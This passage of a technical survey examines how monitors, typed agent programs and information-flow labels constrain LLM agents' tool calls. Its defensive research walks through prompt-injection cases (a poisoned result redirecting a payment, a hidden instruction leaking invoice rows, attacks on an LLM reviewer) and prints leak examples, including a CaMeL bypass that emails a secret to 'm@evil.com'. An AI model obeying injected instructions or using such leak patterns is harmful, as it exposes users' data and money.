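A place that enforces a limit is called a monitor place. (It is part of the net, unlike the run-time monitor, which is a program.) To build one, write the limit as a weighted count of firings:

η₁y₁ + η₂y₂ + … + ηₙyₙ ≤ β

The new place starts with β marks. A transition with a positive weight ηᵢ takes ηᵢ marks from it, one with a negative weight adds |ηᵢ| marks, and one with weight zero is not connected to it. By the state equation, the place always contains β minus the weighted count, which is the unused part of the limit. It cannot contain fewer than zero marks, so the weighted count cannot exceed β.

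For the refunds, the limit is y(*pay*) − y(*approve*) ≤ 0. The recipe produces the Approved place again, which starts empty, gains a mark with each *approve* and loses one with each *pay*. If the budget is ten units, an ordinary search uses one unit and a query to a paid database uses three, the limit is y₁ + 3y₂ ≤ 10, where y₁ counts ordinary searches and y₂ counts paid queries. After three paid queries, one mark is left, so the monitor refuses a fourth paid query but still allows an ordinary search.

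Yamalidou, Moody and colleagues (1996), in *Control of Petri Nets Based on Place Invariants*, gave a version for limits on the marks themselves. In their example, places p₂ and p₃ may hold at most one mark between them, as when two agents must never edit the same file at once. They turn the limit into an equation, μ₂ + μ₃ + μ_c = 1, where μ₂ and μ₃ count the marks in the two places and μ_c, the unused part of the limit, becomes the number of marks in a new place. Transitions t₁ and t₅ bring a mark into the pair, so each must take one from the new place. Transition t₄ removes a mark from the pair and gives one back. Transitions t₂ and t₃ only move marks between p₂ and p₃, so they need no new arrows. In general, the new row of the incidence matrix is −L·D, where D is the old matrix and L lists the limit's coefficients. Moody and Antsaklis (2000) point out that the resulting controllers are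 identical to the "monitors" that Giua and colleagues had derived independently.

Each limit requires one extra place, which takes little more than a matrix multiplication to compute, and the place blocks only steps that would break the limit. This works as long as the monitor can refuse every step that uses up marks. If an outside event can break the limit by itself, a single place is not enough, and someone has to compute a supervisor.

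A monitor place also doesn't ensure that the task can finish. Suppose an agent is allowed six calls to book a flight, and it needs one each to search, hold a seat, charge the card and issue the ticket. If it searches four times, then holds a seat and charges the card, it has no calls left to issue the ticket. The customer has paid and has no ticket, although the agent stayed within its limit.

The monitor should have refused the fourth search. Gu and Zhu's supervisor can do this because it also refuses steps into markings from which the run cannot finish. But they count handing the task to a person as finishing. If the agent can always hand over the task, the supervisor will allow a state in which the card has been charged but there is no ticket, unless the modeller forbids that state. And if the budget counts calls to the model instead of calls to tools, refused proposals also use it up.

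### Coloured marks

Ordinary marks are interchangeable, so an agent could use an approval for a $40 refund to issue one for $4,000. In a coloured Petri net, each mark carries data, called its colour, and a transition can have a guard that compares colours.

Gu and Zhu colour an approval with the digest of the approved file, a short fingerprint computed from its contents. To deploy a file, the agent needs a mark whose digest equals the one that the interface computes from that file. If an attacker changes one line after the reviewer approves a build, the digest changes and no mark matches. The inequality now holds for each digest separately, because the coloured net is equivalent to an ordinary net with one approval place for each digest. Deployments of a build therefore never exceed approvals of that build. The expanded net can be exponentially larger than the coloured one, and the supervisor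 has to cover all of its states, so the data on a mark should be small. An email, for example, could enter the net as a category instead of its full text.

*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) uses coloured marks for payments and other sensitive calls. If the user asks the agent to pay $100 to BillPay, the system creates a mark with that recipient, that amount and one use. A poisoned tool result may lead the agent to propose paying Mallory $100 instead, but no mark matches that call. Tool results go into a separate place for evidence and can never create a permission by themselves. The monitor reserves the mark's use when a payment starts, removes it if the payment succeeds, restores it if the payment is confirmed to have failed, and keeps it reserved while the outcome is unknown.

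Li and colleagues measured what each part of the permission contributes, using 285 unauthorised proposals from two benchmarks. Each row of the table adds one check to the checks in the rows above it.

| What the permission fixes | Wrongly accepted, AgentDojo banking tasks | Wrongly accepted, ASB memory-poisoning tasks |
|---|---|---|
| The tool | 89.29% | 89.05% |
| Where the arguments come from | 84.52% | 79.60% |
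| The stage of the workflow | 45.24% | 39.80% |
| The number of uses | 5.95% | 0.00% |

None of these checks rejected a legitimate proposal. The last two drops are large partly because Li and colleagues added wrong-stage calls and repeats of used-up permissions to the test set. The table shows that each check stops the kind of misuse it targets, but not how common each kind is. In a separate test with Llama 3.3 70B, removing the argument checks raised the attack success rate from 5.1% to 24.0%.

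### Harmful calls with valid marks

All five unauthorised calls that passed every check came from one task, in which the user's own request gave the attacker's account as that of a "new landlord", so the call matched its permission exactly. Gu and Zhu rely on the validator to catch malicious arguments, but they do not analyse it. If a reviewer approves a patch that contains a backdoor, the digest guarantees only that the agent deploys that exact patch.

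ToolFence also has a reviewer, a separate language model that can grant permissions the original request did not cover. Attackers can exploit this reviewer by spreading instructions over many records until a harmful action looks like a necessary step. On AgentLAB, a benchmark of such long attacks, 29.4% succeeded against ToolFence with Qwen3-max, compared with 76.3% without a defence.

Human reviewers are not reliably better. In Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 1,053 paid testers each saw one clearly dangerous command among the permission prompts of a coding session, and only 13.6% blocked it. The rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers were not working on their own projects, and Anthropic published the study to support replacing these prompts with an automatic check. Still, Claude Code users approve 97% of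 permission prompts in real work, which suggests that many do not read them closely.

If every call uses up an approval, the agent has to prompt for a new one each time, and people grow less careful as prompts accumulate. A "don't ask again" button stops the repeated prompts by turning the approval into a condition that calls check but don't use up. It seems better to require single-use approvals only for the few calls that are hard to undo, and to let people review the rest as a plan. Anthropic's users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents, against 3% of individual requests, though some of those rejections are presumably about the work itself rather than safety.

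Even a careful reviewer can miss harm that isn't visible in the tool call. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who wants an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. A hidden instruction leads the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name are all acceptable.

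Hossain and colleagues had 80 people judge similar requests, 20 for each of four displays. People who saw a conventional prompt approved 55.0% of the unsafe requests. Those who saw the user's original instruction and a full log of the agent's steps approved 32.5%. When the display also stated the consequence, for instance that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows, people approved 24.2%, although the study was too small to show that this last improvement was real. Approvals of harmless requests also fell slightly, from 91.7% with the conventional prompt to 85.8%.

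The statement about the raw rows came from a program that records which files the agent derived from which data. When Hossain and colleagues let the program itself block calls, the share of unsafe actions that one agent carried out fell from 43.3% to 5.0%.

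## Plans as typed programs: limits on where data may go

Hossain and colleagues could stop the invoice rows from leaving because their program recorded which data each file came from. Limits on the order of calls don't track where data came from, so an allowed email can still contain a secret. A guard that inspects the message can't reliably find the secret, because the model may have rounded, summarised or translated it.

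*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) makes the same objection to sandboxes, which restrict the files and network addresses a program can reach but don't track data passed from one permitted call to the next.

When the plan is a program, data has to pass through variables to get from one call to the next, so the rules of the language can limit where it goes. (SOTERIA has some value-flow rules for its plan graphs as well.)

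### Four terms on three lines of code

Take this short program, which emails Bob a summary of a company's salary file:

```
notes = readFile("salaries.txt")
body  = summarise(notes)
sendEmail("bob@example.com", body)
```

The *operational semantics* of a language is the set of rules that turns each program into a transition system. A state consists of the code still to run and the current values of the variables. Here, the first step reads the file, stores the text in `notes` and leaves two lines to run.

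A type describes a value, and a checker can work out the type without running the program. Suppose `readFile` returns a `Secret Text`, `summarise` turns one `Secret Text` into another, and `sendEmail` accepts only plain `Text`. If a plan reads a file, summarises it and emails the summary, the checker rejects the email step before any of the plan runs. *Type soundness* means that the properties a type system is meant to guarantee hold in every run of every program it accepts.

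A *capability* is a value that a program must hold to perform some action. If `sendEmail` also needed an argument `mailbox`, and only trusted code could create one, a program without a `mailbox` could not send email.

An *information-flow label* records where a value came from or who may see it. If `notes` has the label "secret", `body` gets the same label because the program computed it from `notes`, and `sendEmail` can reject it. Labels can also keep untrusted data out of sensitive tools. For example, text from a web page gets the label "untrusted", and a payment tool rejects any recipient with that label. Labels also have to account for branches. If a program emails Bob "yes" only when a salary exceeds $100,000, Bob learns something about the salary even though the email contains no secret text.

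### Language-Based Agent Control

Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, have the model write programs in Haskell, a language whose types also specify which effects a piece of code may have, such as writing files. Their library, ELBA, provides one main function:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

The developer supplies the definitions that the model may use, a prompt, and the type `t` of the result. When a running program reaches this call, ELBA prompts the model for a Haskell program, checks that it has type `t`, and runs it. If the check fails, the model gets the compiler's error message and tries again.

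The choice of `t` can itself be a policy. For example, a public calculator can require an `Int`, a whole number. If a visitor asks it to delete all the files on the server and then compute a factorial, the model may write a program that does both. But deleting files has the effect type `IO`, so the whole program does too, and ELBA rejects it.

Most agents need some effects. The main example is an agent that compiles a bibliography and may only write entries that come from DBLP, an online database of computer-science papers. In simplified form, the developer gives it three functions:

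```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

The developer then asks for a program of type `BibIO ()`, which can have these three effects and no others. Only `dblpFetchBib` can produce a `Trusted Bib`, so the model can search, sort and filter as it likes but can't write an entry of its own. Suppose it tries to bypass the database:

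```
writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{smith2026, title={An invented paper}}"
```

ELBA rejects this program before running any of it, because `writeFile` has type `IO ()`. In a test with 100 citation tasks and Claude Sonnet 5, none of ELBA's 925 citations had the wrong authors, year or identifier, compared with 19 of the 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search. The type ensures that the entries are genuine, but not that they are relevant.

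The model's program can itself call `agent`. It might run one search, put the first result into a new prompt, and have a sub-agent write the next part. Because that call sits inside a `BibIO` program, Haskell gives it a `BibIO` type too. A parent can give its sub-agent a narrower type but not a wider one. The plan can therefore grow as results come in, and every new part must pass the same check.

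The soundness theorem makes this precise. For a program e, traces(e) is the set of traces it can produce. A predicate P is a *type system property* for type t if every program e of type t satisfies P(traces(e)). The theorem states that every type system property of a language L still holds when `agent` is added to L. To prove it, Zhou and colleagues give each `agent` call a bound n on how deeply further calls can nest:

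- At depth 0, the call returns nothing.
- At depth n + 1, the call gets a program from the model, in which any further `agent` calls have depth at most n. If the program has type t, it runs. Otherwise the call returns nothing.

The proof then replaces each `agent` call with ordinary code in L that queries the model, checks the reply and evaluates it. Induction on n shows that this changes neither the type nor the traces. The result is a program in L, so P holds for it. The proof works whatever the model writes, provided the type system's guarantees hold. Full Haskell has features that break those guarantees, but ELBA can exclude them by restricting the model to a safe subset of the language.

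For information flow, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library. LIO keeps a current label for the computation, which covers everything the program has read so far. If a program fetches a page from phony.com and then tries to write to the user, LIO stops it with an error. This program passes the type check, and the error comes only at run time, after the fetch and before the write. In a longer program, any calls made before the error have already taken effect.

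The evaluation used the Slack tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides malicious instructions in the data an agent reads. The comparison system was CaMeL, in which the model writes its program before it sees any untrusted data. The table shows how many of the 21 tasks each system completed when there were no attacks.

| Model | ELBA, no policy | ELBA, with policy | CaMeL, no policy | CaMeL, with policy |
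|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT 5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |

With policies enabled and attacks present, ELBA also completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL. But the two systems enforce different policies, so the programming model may not explain the whole difference.

All four models resisted all 105 of the benchmark's own attacks even without a policy, so those attacks could not show whether policies improve security. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated the worst case, in which any sub-agent that reads an injected instruction obeys it. Without policies, 16% to 42% of these attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, none succeeded in 2,940 runs, after a manual review of 29 runs that the benchmark had scored wrongly. Policies also lowered task completion in the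 same test, from 67%–76% to 40%–48%.

### Capture checking in Scala 3

TACIT, a system by Odersky and colleagues, stops leaks of secret data before the agent's code runs. The agent writes short programs in Scala 3, whose experimental *capture checking* records in each type which capabilities a value can reach. A function that takes a string and writes it to the file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where `{f}` is the function's capture set. A function of type `String -> Unit` has an empty capture set, so it can't write to a file, use the network or print.

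TACIT puts secret data into a wrapper called `Classified`. To work on the contents, the agent passes a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which accepts only functions with an empty capture set and wraps the result again. Suppose the agent has opened `outFile` and tries to copy a key into it:

```
val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
key.map { k => outFile.write(k) }
```

The compiler rejects the program, reporting that the capability `outFile` "cannot flow into capture set {}". This happens before either line runs, so the program hasn't read the key. The agent could still use `map` to count the key's characters, but the count would be classified too.

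TACIT treats the agent's own model as a possible attacker. If the agent prints a classified value, the user sees the contents on a separate channel, but the model sees only `Classified(****)`. For language tasks such as summarising a secret report, the program can pass the wrapped text to a second, trusted model and get a wrapped summary back.

In the main safety test, the agent worked on a software project that contained a folder of secrets. The test included 120 trials with injected instructions and 11 in which the user asked for the secrets directly or under a pretext. With the wrapper, neither Claude Sonnet 4.6 nor MiniMax M2.5 leaked anything. Without it, Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 of the 11 trials with malicious requests, and MiniMax leaked them in 8 of those 11 and in 3 of its injection trials. The wrapper didn't reduce the number of ordinary tasks the models completed.

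TACIT also blocked all but one of 1,926 attacks on AgentDojo's four standard sets of tasks. In the remaining run, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another, and the benchmark counted the quotation as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues describe task completion as comparable to CaMeL's, but the rates differed widely in some tests. TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks with o4-mini-high, compared with 81% for CaMeL, and 64% of the travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, compared with 1% for CaMeL.

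Capture checking doesn't prevent every leak. A function passed to `map` could take longer when a secret has a certain value, so an observer could learn about the secret by timing the function. Once the agent starts an external program, the types no longer apply, and protection depends on the list of permitted commands.

### The LLMbda calculus

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) uses labels in LLMbda, a language with no types. LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language whose programs consist of functions and function calls. Its new operator, `@`, sends a prompt to the model, reads the reply as an expression in the language and evaluates it, so a reply can be data or code. `fork` runs an expression in a temporary copy of the conversation, and `clear` empties the conversation.

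In the basic version, a label is a set that can contain U for untrusted and S for secret. The conversation has a label too, which grows to cover everything the program has sent. This program asks the model to put a secret code into a note:

```
let key  = ["S"]:"4471" in
let note = @("Write a short note with the code " + key) in
let _    = assert ["U"] note in
sendNote note
```

The prompt contains `key`, so the conversation gets the label S, and so does everything the model writes in reply. The `assert` lets a value through only if its label is within {U}, meaning the value isn't secret. So the interpreter stops at the third line, after the model has written the note and before `sendNote` runs. It would stop even if the model had spelled the code out in words, because the label doesn't depend on the text. Unlike TACIT, LLMbda lets the model see the secret and controls only what happens to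 the model's reply.

Code the model writes also runs under the conversation's label. If the model has read an untrusted email, any program it then writes counts as untrusted, and so does everything that program returns.

Run-time labels are easy to get wrong, and Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL that works roughly like this:

```
rich, tmp = True, True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
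if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the second line changes `tmp` and labels it secret. The third line does nothing, so `rich` is still true and has no label, and the email goes out. Labels attach only to variables that the program changes, but here the attacker learns the secret from a variable that stayed the same. In LLMbda, a program can change only the conversation in place, and the interpreter stops any program before it adds to a public conversation from a branch that depends on a secret.

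A theorem rules out such leaks for every LLMbda program, including programs that run code from the model. The property is called *noninterference*. Take two runs whose inputs differ only in data that an observer may not see. Because the model's replies are random, each run has a probability distribution over what the observer sees, μ for one and ν for the other. If Δ is the statistical distance between them and div is the probability that a run never finishes or gets stuck, then

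Δ(μ, ν) ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2

If both runs always finish, the observer sees exactly the same distribution from each and learns nothing. If each gets stuck 10% of the time, the distance between the two distributions is at most 0.1. An attacker can therefore learn a little from whether a run was blocked, and more by repeating the run. CaMeL's retry loop makes this repetition possible because it operates outside the label tracking. Garby and colleagues checked their proofs in the proof assistant Lean, and the theorems cover the same interpreter that calls the model.

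Randori, an agent built in LLMbda, practises on mock data before it writes its final program. On AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, with three runs of each, it completed 75% with either GPT-5.2 or Qwen3.7-plus, and 65% with MiMo-v2.5. CaMeL completed 37.5% with its policies on and 67% to 71% with them off. Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and can also make exceptions to them, so part of its advantage comes from looser rules.

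Only 2 of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded, but most of that result can't be attributed to the labels. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a call that the agent's program would never contain. In the other 47, CaMeL without policies stopped every attack with GPT-5.2 and 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. ELBA's test with obedient sub-agents is better evidence for labels, because the model itself did not resist the attacks.

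### Labels that spread until nothing may be sent

The drop in ELBA's completed tasks, from 18 to 10 with Opus 4.7, is an example of a known problem called label creep. A label can only grow as data mixes, so an agent that has read one web page and one private message may soon be unable to pay or write to anyone. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) measured label creep in a simulator, varying the number of agents, their connections and the tools each one had. Network structure strongly predicted how much usefulness was lost (rank correlations reached 0.96), but no design prevented the loss completely.

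The usual remedy is to keep labelled data out of the main conversation. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the dual-LLM pattern, in which the planning model handles untrusted data only as variables whose contents it can't see, and a quarantined model without tools processes the contents. LLMbda can do the same with `fork` and `clear`. In ELBA, a sub-agent can read untrusted data in isolation and return a sealed result. Unlike a quarantined model, the sub-agent can still use any tools its label allows.

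Isolation doesn't help when the task itself requires the flow. If a user asks the agent to pay the bill in an untrusted file, the account number has to get from that file to the payment tool. Garby and colleagues quote an earlier version of the ELBA paper, in which Zhou and colleagues wrote that many tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit" and suggested asking the user to confirm those flows.

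### Declassification and endorsement

Such a task needs a controlled exception. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) distinguishes *declassification*, which permits a specific release of sensitive information, from *endorsement*, which lets a program treat selected untrusted data as trusted for a specified purpose.

LLMbda programs endorse values with the `endorse` operator. A second theorem shows that endorsing untrusted data can never expose secrets, whatever data the attacker chooses. `endorse` also has no effect in code that runs under an untrusted label, so an attacker can't get data endorsed just by making the model write `endorse` after reading a malicious email. This protection fails if the program has already endorsed the malicious text, and Garby and colleagues describe a wrapper that refuses to endorse the same data twice.

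Endorsement is safest when the value comes from a short fixed list. If an agent sorts emails into eight categories and endorses the category, an attacker can choose among eight subject lines for the reply (3 bits) but can't write their own. Endorsing an account number doesn't limit the attacker's choice in this way. Both successful attacks on Randori came from a task in which the agent had to read a file and make the payment described in it, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without `endorse`, the labels block this attack but also block payment of the real bill. Removing `endorse` reduced completed runs from 36 to 30 of 48 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5.

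Declassification requires someone to decide what may be released. In TACIT, unwrapping a classified value requires a capability that a person with clearance may have but the agent never gets. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) uses a content checker that returns only SAFE or BLOCKED, because an explanation could reveal something about the protected records. The system asks the data's owner only when a real authorisation decision remains. This spares people most of the prompts, but if the checker wrongly returns SAFE, the data is released, and no theorem about labels prevents that.

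### The work of typing tools and writing typed code

Someone also has to give every tool a type or a label policy. Odersky and colleagues report that the reusable part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines of Scala. The typed descriptions of the tools for an airline and a shop took a few hundred lines each, about as much as the untyped descriptions they replaced, and models can help write them. The amount of code seems manageable, but a mistake in it can undo the guarantee. If a developer marks a function as safe when it secretly writes to a log, the compiler will accept code that passes classified data to it. *SPA* (2026) similarly criticizes CaMeL because its guarantees depend on someone writing a correct and complete policy for each tool.

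Having to write in unfamiliar languages hurts models less than one might expect. On τ²-bench, a benchmark of customer-service conversations, three open models did slightly better when they wrote typed Scala than when they made ordinary tool calls, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On a set of software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 did slightly worse with Scala, at 41.7% against 43.3%. Between 0.3% and 8% of the Scala programs in the customer-service tests needed a retry, often for mundane reasons such as a dollar sign that Scala parsed as the start of a variable name. ELBA averaged 0.13 retries per run, and only 7 of 2,688 runs used up their retries without producing a program that passed the check. Running time is a bigger problem for ELBA, which took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because its agents call the model again whenever they need to react to new data.

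LLMbda is harder for models to write because its syntax appears nowhere in their training data. In one example, GPT-5.2 needed three attempts to write a factorial function that the interpreter could read. The language also has no type checker, so many mistakes appear only when the program runs. Garby and colleagues suggest adding one, which would catch such mistakes before the program runs and give the model a precise error message to work from.

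## How much each representation can express

A monitor can enforce a rule only if the plan's notation can distinguish runs that obey the rule from runs that break it. An acyclic graph cannot describe a loop that may repeat any number of times, and a finite graph with loops cannot match payments to an unlimited number of approvals. A general programming language can do both, but no checker can then predict in every case what a plan will do.

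### Expressiveness, size and ease of writing

If each tool name is a letter, a complete run is a word, and a plan's trace language is the set of words it allows. With G, N, H and C for Get-Resv, No-Flown, Hours-Diff and Cancel-Resv, the cancellation plan has the trace language {GN, GNH, GNHC}. The run is GN if the passenger has flown, GNH if the booking is too old, and GNHC if the cancellation goes through.

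A notation's *expressiveness* is the set of trace languages that its plans can have. One notation is more expressive than another if it covers all of the other's languages and at least one more. *Assessing the Expressivity of Planning Formalisms through the Comparison to Formal Languages* (Höller, Behnke and colleagues, 2016) used this measure to compare planning notations. The measure leaves out arguments and results, so a guard such as `hrs` ≤ 24 matters only through the sequences of calls it leads to.

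The measure also leaves out size. The refund net has the same language as its equivalent graph but is much smaller, or more *succinct*. Nebel (1999), in *Compilation Schemes*, used "expressive power" to mean how concisely a notation can state planning problems and plans. Neither measure covers ease of writing. *SHOP2* (2011), which describes a planner of that name, reports that people generally find it much easier to translate classical planning problems into hierarchical ones than the reverse, even when restrictions give both notations the same expressive power.

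### Graphs without and with loops

An acyclic graph has finitely many paths, so its language is finite. Conversely, any finite set of words is the language of some acyclic graph. SOTERIA's plans are in this class if a pass through a list counts as one step.

Loops turn the graph into a finite-state machine, and these machines accept exactly the *regular* languages. A plan with loops can let an agent search for flights any number of times before it books one.

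A set of STRIPS actions with a goal also has finitely many states, because each fact is either true or false. But Höller and colleagues proved that STRIPS covers only some of the regular languages. Repeating a STRIPS action immediately changes nothing, since the first application has already made all of the action's changes. So if two reminders to a customer reach the goal, one reminder does too, and no STRIPS description can require exactly two in a row. With *conditional effects*, which depend on the state in which the action runs, STRIPS covers exactly the regular languages. The first reminder can then record "reminded once" and the next one "reminded twice".

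### Behaviour trees

Robot programmers often prefer behaviour trees to finite-state machines because a large machine with many transitions is hard to follow. Biggar, Zamani and Shames (2021), in *An expressiveness hierarchy of Behavior Trees and related architectures*, worked out how much expressiveness programmers give up by making this choice.

The root of a behaviour tree repeatedly sends out a signal called a *tick*, which travels down the tree from left to right. Every node that receives the tick returns Success, Failure or Running. The leaves are conditions and actions. A condition returns Success if it is true and Failure if not. An action returns Success once it has achieved its aim, Failure if it cannot, and Running in the meantime. Two kinds of inner node do most of the work:

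- A *sequence* node ticks its children in order and stops at the first one that returns Failure or Running, passing that value up. It returns Success only if all its children succeed.
- A *fallback* node stops at the first child that returns Success or Running, and returns Failure only if all its children fail.

A tree for cancelling RES123 could look like this:

```
Sequence
├─ Fallback
│   ├─ condition: resv has a value
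│   └─ action:    Get-Resv
├─ Fallback
│   ├─ condition: ok has a value
│   └─ action:    No-Flown
├─ condition: ok is true
├─ Fallback
│   ├─ condition: hrs has a value
│   └─ action:    Hours-Diff
├─ condition: hrs ≤ 24
└─ action:    Cancel-Resv
```

If each call finishes before the next tick, a successful run goes as follows:

| Tick | What the tree finds, going from the left | Call it selects |
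|---|---|---|
| 1 | `resv` has no value | Get-Resv |
| 2 | `resv` has a value, `ok` has none | No-Flown |
| 3 | `ok` is true, `hrs` has no value | Hours-Diff |
| 4 | `hrs` is 12 | Cancel-Resv |

If No-Flown returns false, the condition "`ok` is true" fails at the third tick. The sequence node then returns Failure without ticking the children further right, so the tree never selects Cancel-Resv. A monitor that accepts only the call the tree selects would therefore reject the cancellation. If the tree receives another tick after the cancellation, however, it selects Cancel-Resv again, because none of its conditions checks whether the booking still exists. Putting the whole tree under a fallback node whose first child is the condition "the reservation is already cancelled" fixes this.

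Biggar and colleagues compare notations by how they map inputs to actions. This is a finer measure than the trace language because it includes what the agent observes. A controller is a function f from all the inputs so far, x₀ to xₙ, to an action. It is *reactive* if only the latest input matters, so that f(x₀, …, xₙ) = r(xₙ) for some function r. A plain behaviour tree is reactive because every tick starts again from the root. PLANEX is also reactive because it keeps no record of its progress.

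A reactive controller that reads only present facts about the booking cannot enforce the airline's first rule, because those facts are the same whether or not the agent has made the No-Flown check. The tree above can enforce it by testing conditions such as "`ok` has a value", which depend on what has already happened. The variables store this history, so the tree can be trusted only if the program that writes them can be.

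There are three levels in the hierarchy:

| Notation | What it can remember | A behaviour that the level above it in this table cannot produce |
|---|---|---|
| Plain trees, decision trees | Nothing | |
| Trees with memory nodes | Which children have already succeeded or failed | Do A until it succeeds, then do B forever |
| Trees that write to a variable, finite-state machines | Any fixed number of states | Do A, then alternate between B and C until C fails, then return to A |

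A plain tree cannot express "A, then B forever" because it must pick A whenever the input is the same as at the start. A sequence node with memory skips the children that have already succeeded, until the whole sequence succeeds or fails and the memory resets. With such a node, the cancellation tree shrinks to a single row of three checks, a condition and the cancellation, provided No-Flown returns Failure for a passenger who has flown. But this memory cannot handle the alternation between B and C. If B fails, the whole tree returns Failure, every memory node resets, and the next tick begins with A, whereas the machine would have gone on to C.

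A behavior tree with one variable of its own can imitate any finite-state machine. The variable stores the machine's current state, and each branch tests for one state, performs its action and writes the next state. The tree is harder to read than the machine's diagram, because the order of the branches no longer matters and readers have to work out the possible sequences from the assignments. Biggar and colleagues compare this construction to the proof that programmers can replace every "go to" with loops and extra variables, a result Knuth dismissed as practically meaningless. If the variables take finitely many values, a tool such as BehaVerify can still check the tree automatically.

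The middle level looks attractive for an agent that has to follow a policy, since most procedural rules concern whether a step has succeeded. Its one drawback is that a memory node does not repeat a check that has passed, so if the passenger boards a flight between the check and the cancellation, the tree will cancel anyway.

### Why no finite graph can match unlimited approvals

No finite-state machine can express the rule "never more payments than approvals". Suppose a machine with k states allowed exactly the runs that obey the rule.

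1. Consider the runs that consist only of approvals, from none up to k. There are k + 1 of them and only k states, so two of these runs end in the same state. Call their lengths i and j, with i < j.
2. After j approvals, the rule permits j payments, so the graph must allow j payments from that state.
3. After i approvals, the graph is in the same state, so it allows j payments there too. That is more payments than approvals, which contradicts the assumption.

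The proof assumes that the calls so far determine the state, but any finite graph can be rewritten to satisfy this assumption. A Petri net avoids the limit on finite graphs because a place can hold any number of tokens.

In practice, no company has unlimited approvals outstanding. If there are never more than 1,000, a graph with 1,001 states can enforce the rule. The net's main advantages are then that it stays small and nobody has to choose a limit. *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI* still needs a limit, because Gu and Zhu compute its supervisor over all reachable markings.

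A graph with loops and an ordinary integer variable can also count. With two such variables that it can increase, decrease and compare with zero, it can simulate any computer. SOTERIA's plans have integer variables but stay manageable partly because they have no loops.

### Tasks inside tasks

A hierarchical task network (HTN) describes work at several levels. Its *primitive tasks* are single actions, such as tool calls. Each *compound task* has one or more *methods*, which replace it with a set of smaller tasks. A method may also restrict the order of those tasks or require conditions to hold between them. A planner keeps replacing compound tasks until only primitive ones remain.

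Erol, Hendler and Nau stress in *Complexity Results for HTN Planning* (1994) that this changes which plans count as valid. A STRIPS planner accepts any sequence that reaches the goal, whereas an HTN planner accepts only sequences that the methods can produce. In their example, an agent without a driving licence has to get to New York. A STRIPS planner might have it take driving lessons first, but in an HTN, the method for driving can require the agent to have a licence already. The same difference matters for the agent that upgraded a booking to business class in order to cancel it. A STRIPS planner whose only goal is a cancelled booking would accept the upgrade, but an HTN planner would reject it if no method for cancelling includes an upgrade.

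A method can also contain the task it belongs to, which makes nesting possible. Suppose an agent has to lock records before it edits them and release them in reverse order. The compound task Work then has three methods:

- lock a customer record, do Work, unlock the customer record;
- lock a payment record, do Work, unlock the payment record;
- make the edit.

With nesting, every unlock matches the most recent open lock, at any depth. A Petri net can count the open locks of each kind, but it cannot record the order in which an unlimited number of them were taken. Nesting cannot replace counting either, because a net can require equal numbers of three kinds of call, with all of the first kind before any of the second and all of the second before any of the third, and nesting alone cannot.

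In *Language Classification of Hierarchical Planning Problems* (2014), Höller and colleagues classified HTNs by the formal languages they can produce. If every method puts its tasks in a fixed order, HTNs produce exactly the *context-free* languages, the class that can describe nested brackets. If methods may leave the order open, the steps of different compound tasks can interleave, and HTNs can also produce some languages that are context-sensitive but not context-free, though none beyond the context-sensitive class. Without recursion, HTNs produce only finite languages, as acyclic graphs do.

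### Golog and ConGolog

Golog is a language for controlling robots in which programs can contain conditions, loops, recursive procedures and free choices. De Giacomo, Lespérance and Levesque (2000), in *ConGolog, a concurrent programming language based on the situation calculus*, added parallel processes. As in STRIPS, a separate description gives each action's preconditions and effects. If each tool result updates the facts that later tests read, the cancellation plan becomes:

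```
Get-Resv(rid); No-Flown(rid);
if ok then
    Hours-Diff(booking time, time);
    if hrs ≤ 24 then Cancel-Resv(rid) else nil
else nil
```

Two relations define what a program does. In both, δ is the program that remains to be run and s is the history of actions so far.

- Trans(δ, s, δ′, s′) holds if δ can take a single step in s, after which δ′ remains and the history is s′.
- Final(δ, s) holds if δ may stop in s.

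Each construct has its own rule for both:

| Program | When it can take a step | When it may stop |
|---|---|---|
| nil (nothing left to do) | Never | Always |
| a (an action) | When a's precondition holds; nil remains | Never |
| φ? (a test) | When φ holds; nil remains and the history is unchanged | Never |
| δ₁; δ₂ (in order) | When δ₁ can, or when δ₁ may stop and δ₂ can | When both may |
| δ₁ or δ₂ (free choice) | When either can; the other disappears | When either may |
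| δ* (any number of times) | When δ can; δ* follows whatever is left of δ | Always |
| δ₁ ∥ δ₂ (in parallel) | When either can; the other stays as it is | When both may |

At the start of the cancellation program, Trans allows only Get-Resv. Once Hours-Diff has returned 12, only the inner `if` remains. Trans then allows Cancel-Resv, and Final does not hold, so the agent has not finished. If Hours-Diff had returned 30, Trans would allow nothing and Final would hold.

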